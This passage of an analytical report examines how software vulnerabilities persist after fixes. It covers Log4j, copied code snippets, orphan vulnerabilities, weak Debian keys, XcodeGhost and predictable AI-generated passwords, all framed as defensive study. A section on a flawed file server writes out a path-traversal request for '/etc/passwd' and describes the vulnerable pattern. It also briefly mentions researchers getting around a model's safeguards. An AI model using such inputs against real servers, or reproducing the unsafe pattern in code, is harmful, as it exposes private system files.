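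The hospital's programmers can name Log4j 2.17.1 in the billing program's own project file without waiting for anyone else, and Maven, the tool that assembles the program, will use that version instead. The program may break if the spreadsheet library doesn't work with the newer Log4j, and the change helps only the hospital, because other programs don't inherit it. Overriding a version is also hard to do well. The researchers found 295,951 project files that overrode the version of a library with known flaws. The override avoided at least one flaw in 87% of them, but avoided all the flaws in only 14%. When flaws remained, it was often because the programmer had chosen a version with a different flaw.

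AI-written code in a published library would spread through the same dependency chains. If a model wrote code that generated predictable password-reset links into a login library, developers who use the library would have to wait for its maintainers to release a fix, and developers further down the chain would have to wait longer. The library's name and version number would help people find the affected programs, but only once somebody knew the library contained the code.

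### Why old copies last

Software inherits flaws from its dependencies far more often than it has flaws of its own. In a sample of about 4 million releases on Maven Central, *The Ripple Effect of Vulnerabilities in Maven Central* (2025) found that about 1% had their own vulnerability, while 46.8% inherited one from a dependency. Many of these programs are probably in no danger, because they never use the part of the library that contains the flaw. *On the Effect of Transitivity and Granularity on Vulnerability Propagation* (2023) criticises earlier research for treating every program with a flawed dependency as vulnerable, and instead traces which functions a program calls. But someone has to do that tracing for each program. According to Sonatype, it is often unclear which team should deal with a library nobody deliberately chose.

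The way programmers specify versions also slows the spread of fixes. About 99% of the dependencies on Maven Central name one particular version, such as 2.14.1, rather than a range such as "2.14 or later". With a range, many programs would pick up a fix the next time someone built them. *Mitigating Persistence* found that about 90% of the ranges covering a flawed library already led to a safe version. Almost all of those ranges had no upper limit, though, so they would also let in any future release that broke the program. Naming one exact version protects a program from such releases, so it is usually a sensible choice.

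Some copies of Log4j don't appear in any list of dependencies. Java programs usually come as archive files, which can contain copies of all the libraries the program needs, sometimes inside further archives. A company that buys such a program may never learn that it contains Log4j. The Board found that common scanning methods had trouble detecting these embedded copies, and that Log4j's maintainers had no list of who used their library. Even a company that found a copy often had to wait for the supplier's update.

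In the meantime, some owners deleted the one file in the archive that performed the dangerous lookups. This removed the cause of Log4Shell but left the old version number in place. A scan that checks only version numbers would still flag the program as vulnerable, so such scans can overstate the danger as well as miss it.

Much of the vulnerable Log4j still in use may be in abandoned software. Veracode found that 79% of the time, programmers never update a library after adding it, according to ITPro. Sonatype says that people tend not to revisit these choices until a breach, an audit or an outage forces them to. The clearest case is Log4j 1.x, which about a third of the applications in Veracode's sample still used eight years after its maintainers ended support in August 2015. Owners who had ignored Log4j for years had little reason to notice an update to it in 2021.

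Old container images and devices could also keep the vulnerable Log4j in use for a long time, but there is little evidence on how often they do. A container image is a saved copy of a program with everything it needs to run. If an administrator updates Log4j in a running container but not in the saved image, the old version comes back the next time someone starts the program from that image. A device such as a network camera usually needs an update from its manufacturer, which may no longer make the device. The Board acknowledged that its 90-day review had not reached the medical-device, home-networking and connected-device sectors, whose experience might be different.

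A removed flaw can also return when someone restarts an old image or copies an old service's build file, version numbers included, to start a new one. Sonatype lists copying build files among the reasons that vulnerable downloads continue. Maintainers were still publishing new library versions with Log4Shell fifteen months after the disclosure, though the data doesn't show how many of those libraries had been fixed in between. For 39% of the flaws in *Mitigating Persistence*, at least one new affected version came out in the month the researchers collected their data. A survival curve that treats each repair as permanent would miss any flaws that came back, and so overstate how much has been removed.

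### The Review Board's forecast

In July 2022, the Cyber Safety Review Board predicted that vulnerable copies of Log4j would remain in use for many years, "perhaps a decade or longer". It had gathered information from nearly 80 organisations and individuals.

The download figures allow a rough check. Suppose the vulnerable share kept falling at the average rate between the first month and the middle of 2025, about three and a half years later. The rate would be

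λ = ln(43/13) / 3.5 ≈ 0.34 per year,

which gives a half-life of about two years. At the end of 2031, ten years after the disclosure, the share would be 13% × e^(−0.34 × 6.5), or about 1.4%. If people downloaded Log4j as often as in 2025, that would still mean some 4 million vulnerable downloads a year. Two data points can't establish a trend, and a constant rate is probably optimistic, since the owners who remain are likely to be the slow ones.

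The forecast looks sound, but a handful of forgotten servers would be enough to make it true. Anyone planning a recall would find it more useful to know how many vulnerable systems will remain and how many of them an attacker can reach. Estimates are scarce, though Singh and colleagues cite a December 2023 press report that put the number of potentially vulnerable servers at about 125,000.

Attackers were still trying to exploit Log4Shell in 2025. Singh and colleagues accepted connections to 209 internet addresses in India that hosted no real services, and saved whatever was sent. Nobody had a legitimate reason to contact these addresses, so nearly all the traffic came from people or programs searching the internet for targets. From December 2021 to October 2025, the researchers recorded 704,407 connections that contained a Log4Shell attack, with the highest peak in 2023 and the next highest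 in 2025.

A few machines were responsible for most of the resurgence in attacks years after the fix. About 404,000 of the connections, well over half of the four-year total, came from six addresses in Poland in 2023. In 2025, 24 addresses in Germany produced almost 99% of the traffic. If the operators of those machines had switched them off, the data would have shown attacks dying away, even though just as many systems would still have been vulnerable.

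About 93% of the attempts carried commands to run on the target or to download more software onto it, so most were not harmless surveys. Attackers can send such attempts automatically with almost no effort, so continuing may be worthwhile even if only a tiny fraction of servers are still vulnerable. In 2022 the Board found that attackers were using Log4Shell less than many experts had expected, but it also noted that many organisations did not collect information on such attacks.

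## What happens to flawed code that was copied without a package name?

Programmers also reuse code by pasting it into their own files. They may copy ten lines from a web page, a single file from another project or an entire library. The pasted code often has no name or version number, whereas even a copy of Log4j inside another program's archive usually has both. When someone later finds a flaw in the original, its maintainers can fix their own version, but they can't update the copies and usually don't know where they are.

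### Why a copy is harder to fix than a library

A pasted snippet doesn't appear in a program's list of dependencies, so a scanner that relies on the list will miss it. A new release of the original code won't replace it either. Programmers also rename variables and rearrange lines to suit their own code, so a patch for one copy may not work on another.

Most projects that copy code don't record that it came from somewhere else. He, Mockus and colleagues (2026), in *File-Level Copying Is an Implicit Dependency in Open Source*, collected 690,500 apparent cases of file copying from World of Code, a research archive of nearly all public code. The source was recorded in 4.25% of cases, and the particular version in 1.97%. Almost 29% of the cases were coincidences or machine-generated files, but excluding them would raise the share with a recorded source to 6% at most. Among libraries that programmers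 had copied into their projects, 10.5% had a recorded source and 2.3% had a recorded version.

When code is copied without a package name, a fix reaches the copy only if someone happens to notice it. PointCloudLibrary, a toolkit for processing 3D scans, contained code from the compression library zlib, and a vulnerability in that copy stayed unpatched for nearly nine years. The maintainers of GDAL, a mapping library, patched their copy of the image library LibTIFF three days after a security fix came out, but the fix took at least 61 days to reach the 20,768 projects that depend on GDAL.

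Programmers often have good reasons to copy code. In the few cases where they gave a reason, they had copied about 70% of the libraries because the original was broken or its maintainers were too slow. Some of those copies contain local repairs, so replacing them with the latest official version could break the program.

### A file server that looked safe

*Eradicating the Unseen* (Akhoundali et al., 2025) followed one flawed snippet across GitHub. The snippet is a few lines of JavaScript that run a simple web server, which sends visitors files from a public folder.

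Suppose the public folder is `/home/myapp/`. When a visitor asks for `photo.jpg`, the server joins the two and sends `/home/myapp/photo.jpg`. But in a file path, two dots mean "go up one folder". If a visitor asks for `../../etc/passwd`, the server goes up from `myapp` to `home`, then to the top of the disk, and sends `/etc/passwd`, a system file that lists the machine's user accounts. This is called path traversal, and it lets an attacker read any file that the server program can read. Some versions of the snippet also load the whole file into memory before sending it, so an attacker can crash the server by requesting a file that never ends.

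A programmer who tried this attack in a browser would see it fail, because browsers remove the dots from an address before sending it. The server then receives a harmless request for `/etc/passwd` inside the public folder. The command-line tool curl also removes the dots unless the user adds an option. Attackers can use software that leaves the dots in.

The oldest copy the researchers found dates from 2010, on GitHub's service for sharing snippets. In 2012 a commenter warned that the code was vulnerable. Another repeated the warning in 2014, but someone tested the code and declared it safe. The argument came up again in 2018 and ended the same way. The snippet had also spread to several programming courses and to a page of Mozilla's developer documentation, where it stayed until 2022. Another copy appeared on Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers, on a page with over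 758,000 views. That copy was still flawed when the researchers wrote their paper. They think a working demonstration of the attack would have settled the argument.

### From 40,546 projects to 63 fixes

The researchers built a pipeline to find the snippet, prove that each copy was dangerous, write a patch and tell the maintainers.

| Step | What was left |
|---|---|
| Search GitHub for the function names the snippet uses | 40,546 projects, with 41,870 files |
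| Scan the files with Semgrep | 8,397 suspicious files |
| Start each program in an isolated environment | 4,489 that ran |
| Attack it | 1,756 successful attacks |
| Generate a patch with GPT-4 and test it | 1,600 valid patches |
| Send the maintainers full details | 464 projects |
| Wait for a fix | 63 projects |

Most of the drop from 40,546 to 1,756 was safe code that the keyword search had also caught. To filter it out, the researchers put a file of random text outside the public folder and asked the server for it. If the text came back, the flaw was real. This test gives almost no false alarms, which matters because the next step is to contact strangers about their code.

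The pipeline missed some vulnerable projects. GitHub returns at most 1,000 results per search, and adding more keywords only partly got around this limit. Another 3,908 suspicious programs wouldn't start automatically. When the researchers ran the 30 most popular of these by hand, nine were vulnerable. At that rate, almost 1,200 of the 3,908 would be vulnerable, although the most popular programs may not be typical. The researchers also left out forks, which are copies of a project that other users make on GitHub, and the most popular vulnerable project alone had over 5,200 of them.

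Each program needed its own patch because the code differed from project to project, but the patches were small. Most added five lines that rejected any request containing two dots. (The paper says that 188 of the 1,756 programs had no proven patch, which doesn't match its count of 1,600 valid ones.)

Far more flawed projects dropped out because the researchers never sent them the details. A public warning can alert attackers, and many of the projects seemed abandoned, so the researchers eventually contacted only those with more than five stars (GitHub's version of a "like") and some activity in the past year. They contacted the most popular ones privately. For the rest, they first posted a public message that didn't describe the flaw, and only 70 of 245 projects reacted. If the flaw was still there after 30 days, they sent a pull request with the patch.

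| Group | Fixed | Total | Rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Popular projects contacted by hand | 13 | 31 | 41.9% |
| Projects sent a pull request | 50 | 433 | 11.5% |
| All projects given full details | 63 | 464 | 13.6% |
| All projects with a confirmed flaw | 63 | 1,756 | 3.6% |

The paper's headline fix rate of 14% covers only projects whose maintainers received both an explanation and a patch. It doesn't apply to all the vulnerable projects, because most of their maintainers never heard about the flaw.

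The gap between 42% and 11% also doesn't prove that private contact works better. Popular projects have more people to deal with a report and more to lose by ignoring it. There were only 31 popular projects, so each one moves their rate by about three percentage points. All the rates may also have risen since, because some maintainers were still working on a fix when the researchers counted.

Maintainers accepted 46 pull requests, closed 24, and made no decision on over 360. Of those who closed one and gave a reason, some said they used the code only for testing or development, and two thought the report was spam. Four wrote their own patch instead. Owners of Heartbleed servers had to update a library they already knew about, but here a stranger was asking maintainers to accept a ready-to-merge patch for code they may have pasted in years earlier, and most didn't respond.

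### Chatbots that wrote the same flaw

Akhoundali and colleagues also asked popular chatbots to write a file server without outside libraries, and then attacked the programs they produced. Of 80 programs, 76 had the path traversal flaw. When the researchers asked the chatbots to secure those programs, 42 of the 80 new versions still had it. In a separate round, they asked for a secure server from the start, and 56 of 80 were vulnerable.

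These results are now history. The models included GPT-3.5, which dates from 2022, and the rates say little about what current models write.

The researchers concluded that the chatbots had learned the snippet from public code. That is plausible, but the test can't show whether a model learned the snippet or made the same mistake independently. Joining the folder and the requested name is the obvious way to write such a server, and human programmers had accepted it as safe for years.

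The newer *Security Vulnerability Patterns in AI-Generated Code* (July 2026) found that all its folder-watching programs shared the same type of flaw, path traversal. In those programs, the dangerous path came from a settings file rather than a web visitor, so an attacker would presumably need to change the settings first. The researchers' simplest explanation is that the models settle on similar designs when asked for the same kind of tool. The finding doesn't show how the same models would do on the file-server test.

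### Snippets from Stack Overflow

*Time to Separate from StackOverflow and Match with ChatGPT for Encryption* (2024) cites two very different estimates of how much code on Stack Overflow is insecure. Fischer and colleagues trained a classifier on 1,360 security-related snippets, and it labelled about 30% of 3,834 snippets insecure. Rahman and colleagues searched 529,054 blocks of Python code for six dangerous practices and found them in 3,685, or 0.7%. Much of the difference probably comes from the samples, since most Python code on the site has nothing to do with security. A search for six practices also misses every other kind of mistake.

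What happens after someone copies a bad snippet matters more for a recall. *An Empirical Study of C++ Vulnerabilities in Crowd-Sourced Code Examples* (2019) followed vulnerable C++ snippets from Stack Overflow into GitHub projects. The researchers reviewed 287 files that contained such a snippet. Programmers had corrected the flaw in 34 (12%), and the other 253 were still vulnerable. The researchers recorded only the state of the files when they checked, so their count gives no half-life. Some programmers may have corrected the code as they pasted it in, so the share repaired later may be lower than 12%.

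### Orphan vulnerabilities

An orphan vulnerability is a flaw that survives in a copy after someone has fixed the original. In *The Extent of Orphan Vulnerabilities from Code Reuse in Open Source Software*, Reid, Jahanshahi and Mockus (2022) used World of Code to trace files from three libraries. For every flawed version of a file, they found the projects that had ever contained an identical copy and checked what those projects contained now. The table shows three of their four cases. The libpng library handles PNG images.

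| Flaw | Original fixed | Copy still flawed | Replaced with a fixed version | Changed in some other way | File deleted |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Heartbleed (OpenSSL) | April 2014 | 121 | 3,156 | 211 | not given |
| CVE-2017-12652 (libpng) | August 2017 | 63,441 | 458 | 20,274 | 28,376 |
| CVE-2021-3449 (OpenSSL) | March 2021 | 1,614 | 11 | 1,079 | 253 |

Only 458 projects had adopted a fixed version of libpng, while 63,441 still had the flaw. Other projects had deleted the file, which also removes the flaw, or changed it in some other way. When the researchers looked at ten of the projects that had changed it, eight had fixed the flaw. If that holds for the rest, about 40% of the projects had got rid of the flaw three and a half years after the original fix. Ten projects are a very small sample, but the true figure is certainly well above 458 out of 63,899.

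Heartbleed had almost disappeared from copied code by 2021. Of the 121 projects that still had it, 113 had shown no activity since before the fix came out. Maintainers had seven years to fix one of the most famous software flaws, and a fork can merge the original's changes fairly easily. The third flaw was only months old when the researchers counted, so its numbers mostly reflect the early stage of removal.

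GitHub's Dependabot tool warns projects about flawed dependencies. The researchers checked a sample of recently active projects with the libpng flaw. Dependabot had not reported the flaw in any of those hosted on GitHub, although it had found other problems in several of them. The researchers then offered a patch to 82 projects. Within two weeks, seven had accepted it and one had updated libpng. Two said they would keep the vulnerable code, and the other 72 never replied. The success rate was about 10%, close to the 11.5% for the file server.

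*Large Scale Study of Orphan Vulnerabilities in the Software Supply Chain* (Reid, Rahkema and Walden, 2023) extended the method to 3,615 flawed files. Programmers had copied 3,014 of them, making over 3 million copies in about 719,000 projects. Maintainers later replaced 3.3% of the copies with a fixed version and changed another 2.3% in ways the researchers couldn't classify. The remaining 94.4% never changed.

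Most of these projects were tiny. The median project was active for one month, and 83% of those on GitHub had no stars. The count also includes some files that predate the flaw in the original. So the 94.4% describes the archive, and the share of running programs with the flaw could be much lower.

Half of the repairs took less than 80 days, and a quarter took more than 560. In projects with at least 100 stars, half took over three years. The gap probably arises because popular projects stay active long enough for late repairs, while a project abandoned after a month can only have quick ones. Both medians exclude copies that nobody fixed, so they don't show how long it takes for half of all flawed copies to be repaired.

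A study by He and colleagues, also using World of Code, gives a much more hopeful estimate. It found 17,314 changes in which a programmer had copied a file with a known flaw. In 47% of cases the exact fixed file later appeared in the project, and in 84% someone at least edited the flawed file, so the true share of repairs could lie anywhere between the two. The gap between 3.3% and 47% probably comes from what each team counted. He and colleagues started from the version of each file just before the fix, which programmers who follow the original closely are more likely to have. Reid, Rahkema and Walden included every earlier version and counted every copy, including those in abandoned projects. Even in the more hopeful data, visible repairs had a median delay of 640 days.

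The main obstacle to fixing these copies may be a lack of people. *Did You Forkget It?* (2025), a study of forks that had missed security fixes, concludes that many of the flaws would be easy to fix but that the forks have too few maintainers. Not every flawed copy matters, though. The maintainer of a Sony version of the Linux kernel, built for ARM processors, pointed out that flaws specific to x86 processors don't affect it, even where the flawed code is present.

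### How closely AI-written code resembles a copy

AI-written code is hard to fix for many of the same reasons as a pasted snippet, but most orphan vulnerabilities seem to come from copying whole libraries. In the 2023 study, about 95% of the copied files were in the same folders as in the original project. Someone who recognises such a library can look up the official fix, whereas AI-written code has no original to consult.

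An AI model can also repeat a mistake in different code. Kordonsky and colleagues found that each coding model tends to produce particular security flaws, and they measured how often those flaws reappeared. On average, flaws recurred about 18 percentage points more consistently across unrelated kinds of application than within one kind. The same mistake could therefore turn up in a shop's checkout and a clinic's booking page that share no lines of code. The method used in the orphan studies would miss both cases because it matched identical files.

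AI tools can also copy flaws in the older sense. *SoK* (2025), a study of security problems in AI coding tools, tested whether models shown 200 vulnerable functions would reproduce the flaws. The results ranged from loose imitation of the style to exact replication, and varied sharply with the type of flaw. If a programmer asks a model to extend a project that already contains the file-server snippet, the model might add another copy. Nobody could then say with confidence whether the flaw came from the model or the project.

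The file-server study is the closest precedent for a recall, because its search allowed for differences in the text. A similar search for the predictable password-reset links might look for files that mention password resets and call a weak random-number function. The searchers could then run each program, request a few links and check whether they can predict the next one. This method works only if the flaw involves recognisable function names and a safe, automatic test can confirm it. It wouldn't work for a page that shows private records without checking who is asking, because that flaw is a missing line, which leaves no keyword to search for. Outsiders could search only public code, so companies would have to check their private projects themselves.

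## What happened when the flaw lay in the tool that produced the output?

Owners removed Heartbleed and Log4Shell by updating the software that contained the flaw. When the flaw lies in a tool that makes other things, updating the tool only protects what it makes from then on. If a factory fixes a machine that drills holes in the wrong place, the parts it has already shipped still have bad holes. Likewise, fixing an AI model that writes flawed code doesn't fix the code it has already written.

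The best-documented case began in 2006, when programmers accidentally broke the part of an encryption library that makes secret keys. As in the password-reset example, an attacker could predict the random numbers.

### How Debian's keys became predictable

Debian is a free, Linux-based operating system that many servers run. Its maintainers distribute their own edited copy of OpenSSL, the library that later had the Heartbleed bug. In September 2006 they changed that copy to stop a warning from Valgrind, a tool that checks how programs use memory. *When Private Keys are Public* (Yilek, Rescorla and colleagues, 2009) explains that the change also removed almost all the randomness from the numbers that OpenSSL produced.

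A server's private key comes with a matching public key that anyone can see. OpenSSL calculates both from random numbers. To make those numbers unpredictable, it mixes in blocks of data that an attacker can't guess, such as noise that the operating system collects. After the change, it mixed in only the length of each block, so 32 bytes of noise had the same effect as 32 zero bytes.

The main thing that still varied was the process ID, a number that the operating system gives each running program. It had 32,768 possible values, so on a given type of machine OpenSSL could make only 32,768 different key pairs of a given size. Yilek and colleagues allowed for three types of machine and three ways in which OpenSSL might treat a particular settings file, which gave

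32,768 × 3 × 3 = 294,912

possible key pairs for each size. An attacker could generate all of them in hours or days. After that, finding a server's private key only meant looking up its public key in the list.

Debian announced the flaw on May 13, 2008, and released a corrected OpenSSL. Debian's *CVE-2008-0166* gives the exact range of faulty versions, so an owner could easily tell whether a server needed the update. But the update did not fix keys the old version had already made, and a key made on a faulty machine remained just as weak when copied to a server that had never run Debian. As after Heartbleed, owners had to replace the key and usually the certificate. Debian provided testing tools and lists of bad keys to help them find the weak ones.

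### Six months of daily scans

Yilek and colleagues started scanning on May 17, 2008, four days after the announcement. They took 59,100 internet addresses that people on the University of California, San Diego network had recently connected to, and tried each about once a day for 173 days. Of these, 51,838 answered at some point, and 751 had a weak key.

By the last day, the owners of 507 servers had switched to a strong key, 206 servers still had a weak one, and 38 had stopped answering. The paper reports that 30% were still vulnerable after almost six months, but its counts give 27%, or 32% if the servers that stopped answering kept their weak keys. The scans missed the first four days, but records from VeriSign, a leading certificate issuer, suggest that few of its customers replaced weak keys in that time.

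Removal looks slower if we count certificates instead of servers. Some companies use one certificate on many servers, so the researchers also grouped the servers by certificate. Owners had not fixed 49% of the 473 groups by the end, which makes the half-life about six months.

The two measures differ because companies with several servers acted faster. The researchers compared owners using a hazard ratio, which is how likely one group is to make a change at any moment relative to another. The ratio was 1.77 for certificates on several servers compared with those on one, and 0.41 for self-signed certificates, which owners issue to themselves, compared with certificates from large issuers. People often use self-signed certificates on test machines and other servers of little value. These certificates made up 2% of the survey but 44% of a random scan by the same researchers, so owners across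 the internet may have acted more slowly than those in the survey.

Owners installed most Heartbleed patches within about two weeks, but they replaced weak Debian keys slowly and steadily. Replacement sped up relative to the normal rate of certificate changes until about day 45, and owners were still replacing keys after five months.

Part of this steady decline came from routine certificate renewal. Certificates at the time typically lasted one or two years, and 34% of all the servers in the survey changed theirs during the scans. An owner who renewed a certificate with a new key, made on an updated machine, would have replaced the weak key without hearing about the problem. Merged code does not expire, so a recall of it would not get this help.

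The researchers also suggest that delay may have been reasonable. An ordinary vulnerability is most dangerous just after its announcement, when attackers rush to use it. With a weak key, an attacker who is recording traffic gains a little more each day, so there is no obvious deadline for replacing the key. Owners of code that leaks a little information every day could justify delay in the same way.

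In 34 cases, a server's owner replaced its certificate but was no safer, because the new one also contained a weak key. In 24 of these, the original issuer or a different one had certified the same key again. In seven others, the owner had made a new key that was also weak, presumably on a machine that still had the faulty OpenSSL. One site changed its certificate 55 times, and the first ten certificates were all weak. Yilek and colleagues concluded that issuers either didn't always check for weak keys or missed some.

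Someone who asks a flawed model to rewrite its own code could end up like the owners of those seven servers.

### Keys that survived until 2024

Sixteen years after the announcement, domains belonging to Cisco, Oracle and other well-known companies still had weak Debian keys. Böck (2024), in *16 years of CVE-2008-0166*, found them in DKIM, a system for proving that an email comes from the domain it names. The domain's owner publishes a public key, and the mail server signs each message with the matching private key. Anyone who could look up the private key could sign forged emails in the company's name.

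Böck checked a list of the million most popular domains and collected 355,055 published DKIM keys of the RSA type, which almost everyone uses. Of these, 855 (0.24%) were weak Debian keys. Only 22 of the weak keys were different, so far fewer than 855 separate repairs were needed. One key appeared 777 times, mostly because domains pointed to a record belonging to the company Cakemail. Böck's email to Cakemail's published security address bounced, but the company later appears to have replaced the key, which would have fixed most of the 777 records at once.

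He suspects that many companies set up DKIM around 2007, when its specification came out, and haven't changed it since. DKIM doesn't require anyone to change keys. Certificate issuers for websites have to reject keys they know are compromised, but nobody does that check for DKIM.

The Czech email provider Seznam at first dismissed his report because Seznam wasn't using the key in question. But the public half was still published, so an attacker could have used the key to forge emails. Seznam has since fixed the problem. An owner could make the same mistake in a recall by ignoring an old password-reset page that still works even though nothing links to it anymore.

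### Infineon's chips and an altered copy of Xcode

Estonia found its weak keys much more easily. In October 2017, researchers led by a team at Masaryk University in the Czech Republic published details of a flaw called ROCA in software for Infineon's security chips. An RSA key depends on two secret prime numbers. Infineon's software generated them faster by picking primes with a particular structure, but that structure could let an attacker work out the private key from the public one.

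About 750,000 Estonian identity cards contained the affected chips. Estonians use these cards to sign documents and log in to public services and banks. The government suspended the cards' certificates on November 3, 2017, and let holders update them online or in person. Most cards didn't need replacing, because the chips could also make a type of key that didn't have the flaw.

Estonia could trace its cards as a carmaker traces cars, because every card had a number and a registered holder. It could also disable the old certificates without waiting for holders to act. The structure that weakened the keys also made them easy to detect. Böck's slides for *16 years of CVE-2008-0166* (2024) list both ROCA and the Debian flaw among the problems that his free tool badkeys can detect from a public key.

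XcodeGhost, which came to light in September 2015, was a deliberate attack. Someone altered copies of Xcode, Apple's program for building iPhone apps, and put them on Chinese file-sharing sites, where developers could download them faster than the original from Apple. The altered version added code to every app built with it, and the app then sent information about the user's phone to the attacker's server. WeChat, the Chinese messaging app, was among those affected. According to emails that became public in Epic Games' lawsuit against Apple, the attack affected about 2,500 apps, which some 128 million people had downloaded.

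A developer who reviewed their own code would have found nothing wrong, because the altered tool added the malicious part later. The repair was simple because that code was clean. The developer could install the genuine Xcode, rebuild the app and send users an update. Apple could remove infected apps from its store in the meantime, although copies already on phones stayed there until their owners updated or deleted them.

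Neither repair works as well for AI-written code. Any properly generated key can replace a weak one, because a key only has to be unpredictable. Developers hit by XcodeGhost still had clean source code to recompile. With AI-written code, the flaw is in the source code itself, and the replacement has to do everything the old code did. Someone could save the original request and give it to a corrected model, but the model might write a different program, which the owner would have to test again.

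### Passwords that language models make up

Language models can produce predictable secrets too. In February 2026, the security firm Irregular published tests in which it asked several models to make up passwords. A proper password generator picks each character at random, with every character equally likely, but a language model picks what is likely to come next, so its choices are far from even.

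Irregular's *Vibe Password Generation* reports that 50 separate requests to Claude Opus 4.6 produced only 30 different passwords. One of them, `G7$kL9#mQ2&xP4!w`, came up 18 times. Raising the setting that controls randomness to its maximum made little difference, and the same password appeared twice in ten further attempts.

Security researchers usually measure password strength in bits of entropy, and each extra bit doubles the number of guesses an attacker needs. A character chosen at random from a set of 70 has log₂(70), or about 6.13, bits, so a random 16-character password has about 98 bits. Irregular calculated the entropy at each position from the 50 passwords and got a total of about 27 bits.

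Even 27 bits overstates how safe the passwords are. It would normally mean over a hundred million guesses, but in this sample an attacker's first guess would have been right 36% of the time. Irregular estimated that a 20-character password from OpenAI's GPT-5.2 had about 20 bits, based on the probabilities the model assigned to each character. It should have had over 120.

The pattern only appears when someone compares many passwords from the same model. Common strength checkers rated the Claude passwords as excellent because they had capitals, digits and symbols in no obvious order.

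Coding agents, which can run commands as well as write code, have proper password generators available but don't always use them. When Irregular tested Claude Code, Anthropic's coding tool, with Opus 4.6, it usually ran a generator when asked to "generate" a password but made one up when asked to "suggest" one. Agents can also make up a password while setting up a database, without the developer asking for one. Anthropic and OpenAI have since released newer models, which may behave differently, but passwords from the older ones could still be in use.

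### How many of these passwords are on GitHub?

GitGuardian, which sells tools for finding leaked passwords, tried to count passwords generated by language models. It generated 200 passwords with each of 40 models and used them to train Markov chains. A Markov chain records the probability that one character follows another. If `7` is often followed by `$` in one model's passwords, a password containing `7$` is a little more likely to have come from that model. Multiplying these probabilities along the password gives an overall score.

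GitGuardian tested the chains on a new set of model-written passwords. The chains identified the right model 55% of the time and the right provider 65% of the time. The company then scored 34 million passwords that people had put on GitHub between November 2025 and March 2026. Accepting only high-confidence matches, it classified about 28,000 as model-written.

GitGuardian doesn't report how often its method flags a password that no model wrote, which is the more important error. The 28,000 flagged passwords are 0.08% of the total, so if the method wrongly flagged one ordinary password in 1,200, false alarms could account for all of them. The method may also have missed many model-written passwords, and GitGuardian doesn't report that rate either.

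Some of the matches are probably right. Of about 8,700 commits (saved sets of changes) containing a password suspected to come from an Anthropic model, 41 named Claude as a co-author. That is under 0.5%, but GitGuardian notes that the label is optional and that people may have pasted in passwords they got from a chatbot. The company concluded that the problem was not widespread. It sells tools for catching such passwords, so it had little reason to play the problem down.

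More than half of Irregular's passwords from Claude Opus 4.6 began with a capital G, but GitGuardian found that Claude Opus passwords always began with a lower-case letter. The difference may come from how each firm sent its requests. If so, a detector trained on one setup could miss passwords the same model wrote in another.

Irregular advised security teams to audit and replace any password that a model or coding agent may have generated. This is close to a recall notice, though it came from an outside firm and not from the companies whose models wrote the passwords. The advice is practical because replacing a password takes so little work that a team can do it even when unsure who created it, while few teams could rewrite all their code of uncertain origin.

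### When Claude's output got worse

Anthropic has published two detailed accounts of faults that made its products give worse answers, including worse code. It did not tell users in either account to recheck code they had already received.

Anthropic's *A postmortem of three recent issues* (2025) describes three bugs in the systems that run its models, all from August and September 2025:

- From August 5, some requests to Claude Sonnet 4 went to servers set up for much longer conversations. The bug affected 0.8% of the model's requests at first and 16% in the worst hour. About 30% of the people using Claude Code in this period had at least one message sent to the wrong servers.
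- From August 25, a faulty setting sometimes made several models insert characters that didn't belong, such as Thai letters in an English answer or obvious syntax errors in code.
- A separate change that week could make a model skip the word it considered most likely. Anthropic confirmed this for Claude Haiku 3.5 and suspected it for two other models.

A syntax error is usually easy to notice because the program won't run. An answer from the wrong server might just be a worse program than the user would otherwise have got, with nothing in the code to reveal it. Anthropic's tests missed the decline, partly because Claude often recovers from isolated mistakes. Anthropic's privacy rules also limited when engineers could look at users' conversations. Similar rules could make it harder for a developer to work out who had received flawed code.

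Anthropic's *Model output quality* (2025), the notice on its status page, marked the incident resolved on September 17. The bugs were gone, but any poor code users had merged in the meantime was still there.

The 2026 faults were in Claude Code and related products, and programs that connected directly to the models were unaffected. Anthropic's *An update on recent Claude Code quality reports* traces complaints from users to three changes:

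| Introduced | Change | Reversed or fixed |
|---|---|---|
| March 4 | Claude Code spent less effort on reasoning by default | April 7 |
| March 26 | A bug kept deleting the model's earlier reasoning from some sessions | April 10 |
| April 16 | A new instruction told the model to keep its messages short | April 20 |

Anthropic found that the short-message instruction reduced scores by 3% on one of its tests. It compensated subscribers by resetting their usage limits.

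Nolan (2026), in *Anthropic says engineering missteps were behind Claude Code's monthlong decline*, reports a much larger estimate from Dave Kennedy, who runs the security company TrustedSec. Kennedy said his team had measured a 47% drop in the quality of Claude's code, based on defects, security problems and unfinished tasks. He warned that inexperienced developers would not catch the flaws. Nolan doesn't explain how the team calculated the 47% figure, and it isn't comparable with the 3%, which came from a single test of a single change.

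The article also cites tests by Veracode in which Claude Opus 4.7 introduced a vulnerability in 52% of coding tasks, against about 30% for OpenAI's models. The older Claude Opus 4.1 and Sonnet 4.5 had done so in 51% and 50%, which suggests that Claude's code was about as insecure as before. The tests therefore provide little evidence about the faults in March and April.

Perhaps Anthropic had no useful advice to give. It had not identified a particular flaw that users could search for, and rechecking several weeks of work would have taken users a lot of time for an uncertain benefit. But Kennedy's warning applies to people who wouldn't have reviewed the code properly the first time. Anthropic didn't suggest in its account that users recheck their programs, though the dates and affected models it gave could help them decide which ones to recheck.

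Anthropic suspended Claude Fable 5 in June 2026 for an unrelated reason. According to Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026), the US government imposed export controls on the model on June 12, three days after its release. Researchers at Amazon had found a way around its safeguards and got it to identify software vulnerabilities. The order barred foreign nationals from using the model. Anthropic couldn't check users' nationalities in real time, so it cut off everyone. Access returned on July 1.

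The announcement doesn't mention rechecking Fable 5's code, and it had no reason to, since nobody had claimed the code was faulty. But the suspension does show how quickly a company can withdraw a model from all its users.

### Which outputs could anyone recognise?

In the older cases, people could recognize the faulty tool's output even if they had never used the tool. This is harder with language models.

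| Case | Could someone recognise faulty output by inspecting it? |
|---|---|
| Debian keys | Yes, by looking up the public key in a list |
| Infineon keys | Yes, with a mathematical test of the public key |
| XcodeGhost apps | Yes, but only in the finished app |
| Model-written passwords | Sometimes, with an unknown number of false alarms |
| Claude, August–September 2025 | Stray characters and some syntax errors, but not answers that were merely worse |
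| Claude Code, March–April 2026 | No known marker |

Debian's weak keys were easy to list because researchers could rerun the faulty OpenSSL with each process ID and get the same keys it had given everyone else. Nobody could do this for a language model's code, because the output depends on the wording of the request, the files already in the project and chance. A developer that had kept the flawed model could still use it to generate a password-reset page a thousand times and look for what the results had in common. Searching for those common features would help find typical flawed code but would miss unusual versions.

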